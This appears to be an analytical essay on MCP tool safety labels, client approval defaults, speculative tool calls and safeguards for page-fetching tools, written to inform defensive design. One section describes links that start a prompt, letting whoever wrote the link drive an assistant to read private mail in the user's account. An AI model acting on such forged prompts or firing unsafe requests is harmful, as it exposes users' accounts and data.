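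`open_page` is a problem even when its author is honest, although most of this debate concerns dishonest or careless authors. The author can check that the tool's code only sends a GET request and returns the text, but whether anything changes depends on the address the model supplies and on how someone else's server handles the request. OpenAI tells app developers to set `readOnlyHint` on a tool that "only retrieves or lists data" and changes nothing outside ChatGPT. `open_page` always meets the first condition, but it meets the second only when the site follows the HTTP standard.

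An annotation applies to the whole tool, so `open_page` has the same label whether the model opens `/articles/42` or `/articles/42?do=delete`. `openWorldHint` does little to correct this, because the MCP blog suggests using it to scrutinize what comes back from the outside world, not what the request does there. A working group that includes people from Microsoft, OpenAI and Anthropic is considering whether clients or servers should evaluate some annotations when a tool is called. That would at least let a page-opening tool's label depend on the address, though nobody can reliably identify an unsafe GET by its address.

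### When clients skip the question

To find out what clients do by default, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, used AI coding agents to trace tool calls through the source code of 41 popular open-source programs, including 25 applications and 16 toolkits for building agents.

| What happens before an ordinary tool call | Programs |
|---|---|
| The program asks the user | 7 |
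| Codex CLI decides from the annotations | 1 |
| Qwen Code has a language model decide | 1 |
| Nothing | 32 |

At least two of these programs use the read-only label to decide whether to ask the user for permission. Microsoft's editor VS Code normally asks before running a tool, but not if the tool is marked read-only. Codex CLI, the command-line version of Codex, doesn't ask if a tool's annotations mark it as read-only and not destructive. It also doesn't ask about a tool that can make changes if the annotations mark those changes as not destructive and limited to a closed system.

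*The Writes Mode* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a stricter mode in Codex called "writes". In this mode, Codex still runs read-only tools without asking, but it treats an unlabeled tool as one that writes, and a destructive label overrides a read-only one. It also asks again at each write, so approving one call doesn't approve the next.

A false label makes no difference in the 32 programs that run tools without requiring approval, because they also run tools marked destructive. This group includes all 16 toolkits, though most of them let the developer of the finished application add an approval step. It also includes 16 of the 25 applications, and correcting every label would change nothing for their users until the application started to read the labels.

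Asking for permission more often can frustrate users. Users complained in the OpenAI forum thread *MCP Annotations Being Ignored* that ChatGPT was requesting confirmation for tools they had labeled read-only. One found it tedious to keep allowing "harmless read-only queries".

Yao and colleagues estimated the trade-off by pairing 269 destructive tools with each of the 25 applications. By default, 60.7% of the pairs had no enforced approval. If every application asked for approval unless a tool's label declared it read-only or non-destructive, that share would fall to 5.4%. But for tools that had looked destructive and were not, the share of pairs in which the application asked would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%.

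### How often the labels are wrong

The remaining 5.4% consists of destructive tools that were annotated as safe and whose servers did not prompt for confirmation. This is the closest figure to an error rate for these labels. It rises to at least 10.6% when the estimate includes destructive tools that the researchers' software failed to flag.

Neither number is the error rate of `readOnlyHint` alone. Both include tools labeled as making changes but not destructive ones. Both leave out tools that are labeled read-only but add a harmless record, because Yao and colleagues counted only serious actions such as deleting data, sending messages and moving money. Human reviewers also thought the study's AI coders sometimes called a reversible action destructive, so some of these reassuring labels may be right.

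The study measures the share of destructive tools that have safe labels. The share of tools labeled read-only that change something would be more useful to a client, but calculating it from the study's result requires knowing how common each kind of tool is.

*Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) compares tools' written descriptions with their code. Its software, DCIChecker, uses a language model to look for agreement between the two and, separately, for disagreement, then runs a further check if the results conflict. It found a mismatch in 1,907 of 17,030 tools, or 11.2%. Most of these tools did less than their descriptions promised, or something different. In about a quarter of them (roughly 470 tools, or 2.8% of those audited), the main problem was an undeclared side effect, a category that includes heavy resource use and data leaks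 as well as state changes.

The true figures may be lower. DCIChecker's published accuracy in a test on 400 real tools implies that it wrongly flagged 8 of the 203 tools with accurate descriptions. At that rate, about 600 of the 1,907 reported mismatches would be false alarms, and the real share of mismatches would be nearer 8%.

Some mismatches are serious. One tool's description said that a user would have to approve each order on a financial exchange, but the code submitted orders without approval. Others resemble the log entries that the HTTP standard allows. In the paper's opening example, a weather tool also saves the city in a usage history and reports the query to an analytics service.

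Labels can also be correct by accident, or missing. Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, collected the annotations of 98,291 tools without calling any of them. The most common combination, found on 39.9% of the tools, was read-only, non-destructive, repeatable and open-world. But most of those tools came from one publisher, which accounted for 45% of the collection and evidently used a template. Among the remaining tools, 7.3% had that combination and 47.2% had no annotations.

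*What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) found no annotations on 58.8% of tools in a random sample of servers that run on the user's own computer. Of the 194 working servers with tools, 72 labeled every tool and 122 labeled none. If the client follows the cautious defaults, a missing label is safer than a false one, because the user only gets an unnecessary permission prompt. But frequent prompts put pressure on tool developers to mark a tool read-only just to stop the prompts.

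### Running a tool call before the model makes it

Automatic approval saves the user's time. Developers have also used the idea that reads are harmless to reduce the time an agent spends waiting for its tools. *SPORK* (2026) measured tool execution at 16% to 37% of total running time on three benchmarks. In speculative tool execution, a system predicts the agent's next call and runs it early. *Speculate While You Reason* (2026) describes the usual method, in which the system keeps the result and uses it if the agent then makes exactly the same call.

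Yu, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *TomasuLLM*, apply this to coding agents, which can wait minutes for a set of tests to finish. Their system works like this:

1. It drafts actions that the agent may take later.
2. It runs them in isolated sandboxes, where a command that changes a file changes only a copy.
3. It traces what each action depended on and what it changed.
4. It checks each result against the accepted state of the work, and accepts valid results in the order in which the agent would have produced them.

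The system was 1.31 times as fast on 100 software repair tasks from SWE-bench Verified, which would cut a 100-minute job to about 76 minutes. It was 1.35 times as fast on 28 command-line tasks, and on 18 longer sessions it reached the same progress 1.27 times as fast.

TomasuLLM can run a command speculatively without first establishing that it is harmless. If the guess was wrong, the system can discard the sandbox and undo any file deletions, because everything the command touched was inside the sandbox. A live fetch reaches a server outside it, and discarding the response does not restore a page that the fetch caused the server to delete. *AOSpec* (2026) therefore does not speculatively execute actions whose effects it cannot isolate.

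Other systems rely on sorting the tools. *Optimizing Agentic Language Model Inference via Speculative Tool Calls* (2025) has a smaller, faster model guess the calls while the main model is still working, and restricts guessing to tools that are "stateless" and "cheap". It gives web search and file access as examples. *Speculative Interaction Agents* (2026) uses a hand-made classification in which tools that only read information may run early, while those that modify something wait for a final signal.

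A search that reads an index can fairly be called "stateless", but calling `open_page` stateless would repeat Google Web Accelerator's assumption that fetching a link changes nothing. Suppose a user asks an assistant what an email is about, and the email contains a one-time confirmation link. The small model predicts that the assistant will open the link, so the system sends the GET. The main model then outputs a question asking the user whether to open it. The system discards the page it fetched, but the site has already recorded the confirmation.

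Speculation is safer than prefetching in that even a small model can read the word "Delete" and predict a different request. But the tool sends the predicted request before the stronger model has finished deciding, so the stronger model can't prevent it. Browsers now label their prefetches and withhold cookies when prefetching from other sites. A speculative fetch looks like any other request unless the tool's developer adds similar precautions.

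The system cannot always undo a wrong guess. Trofimov and Novikov describe an agent that pursues two plans at once. One provisionally reserves a meeting room, and the other sends invitations naming that room. If the system drops the first plan and cancels the room, the invitations have already gone out. Wrong guesses also add to the load on other people's servers. If several small models each guess a different page, the system requests every page and the agent uses at most one.

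### Links that start a prompt

Some AI assistants accept a prompt in a URL on their own site, such as `https://assistant.example/new?q=Summarize+my+unread+mail`. In some designs, opening the link only fills in the text box, and the user still has to press a button to send the prompt. In others, the link is unsafe because opening it runs the prompt.

If opening a link starts a prompt, the model acts in the user's account on instructions from whoever wrote the link. It may use up part of a paid allowance or call tools, and if the client approves read-only tools automatically, it may read private mail without the user confirming it. This works like cross-site request forgery, except that one forged request can lead to many tool calls.

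Which software can trigger such a link depends on how the page works. If JavaScript on the page submits the prompt, a link checker that only downloads the page won't trigger it, but a browser that prerenders the page might. A page that fills in the box and waits for the user to submit the prompt avoids both problems, but requires an extra click.

### What each safeguard stops

The table compares safeguards for a retrieval tool. "Yes" means the safeguard prevents the failure, and "afterwards" means it only helps people find out what happened.

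| Safeguard | Unsafe GET, logged out | Unsafe GET, logged in | One-time link | Leaked data | Server load | Cost in usefulness |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS | no | no | no | slightly | no | some reads fail |
| No credentials | no | yes | no | partly | no | no private pages |
| Stored copies only | yes | yes | yes | yes, to the site | mostly | old or missing pages |
| Public-address check | partly | partly | mostly | mostly | no | trouble with new or unlisted pages |
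| User confirmation | partly | partly | mostly | partly | partly | interruptions |
| Request logs | afterwards | afterwards | afterwards | afterwards | afterwards | little for the user |

The method limit does badly here because every failure in the table can happen with a GET. It already stops the ordinary purchases, posts and deletions that need another method. It gets "slightly" for leaks because it blocks request bodies, which can hold a whole file, while most servers and tools limit the length of an address.

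Without the user's credentials, a retrieval tool that follows an unsafe link in an account will usually reach only a login page. Withholding credentials also reduces leaks, because a model can't pass on mail it can't open, though the conversation may contain private information that could still leak. It also makes the tool much less useful to anyone who wants help with their own bookings or documents.

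Stored copies hide the query from the site, though not from the company that runs the index. They reduce the site's load because one crawler visit can serve many readers, but a crawler that collects pages nobody asks about may increase it. Stored copies are least suitable for shopping and booking, which need current pages.

The public-address check blocks newly composed addresses and most one-time links, but not a deletion link that a crawler has already recorded. It also helps inside an account, because an address like `/notes/42/delete` is unlikely to appear on a public page, though `/logout` often does. The check doesn't reduce server load, and it can block a page the user wants if the page was published that morning.

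How well user confirmation works depends on what the person can tell from the question. Someone who sees `/r/8841` can't tell that it deletes an article. A one-time link is easier to judge, because people usually remember whether they asked to join a mailing list or reset a password. A leak is harder to spot when the private data is encoded in a long address. Confirmation reduces server load only by slowing the tool down, and approving a whole site at once removes that delay. People who are asked often may also start approving requests without reading them.

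Reviewing logs can't prevent a harmful request, but it can help someone limit the damage sooner. OpenAI advises Codex users to review the agent's work log, where an unexpected address may be the only sign that something went wrong. The log shows what the agent requested but not what the server did in response, so someone still has to check the site. They may be in time to restore a deleted wiki page, but they can't recall a leaked email. The log will also contain any private data that was in the addresses, so whoever keeps it has another copy to protect.
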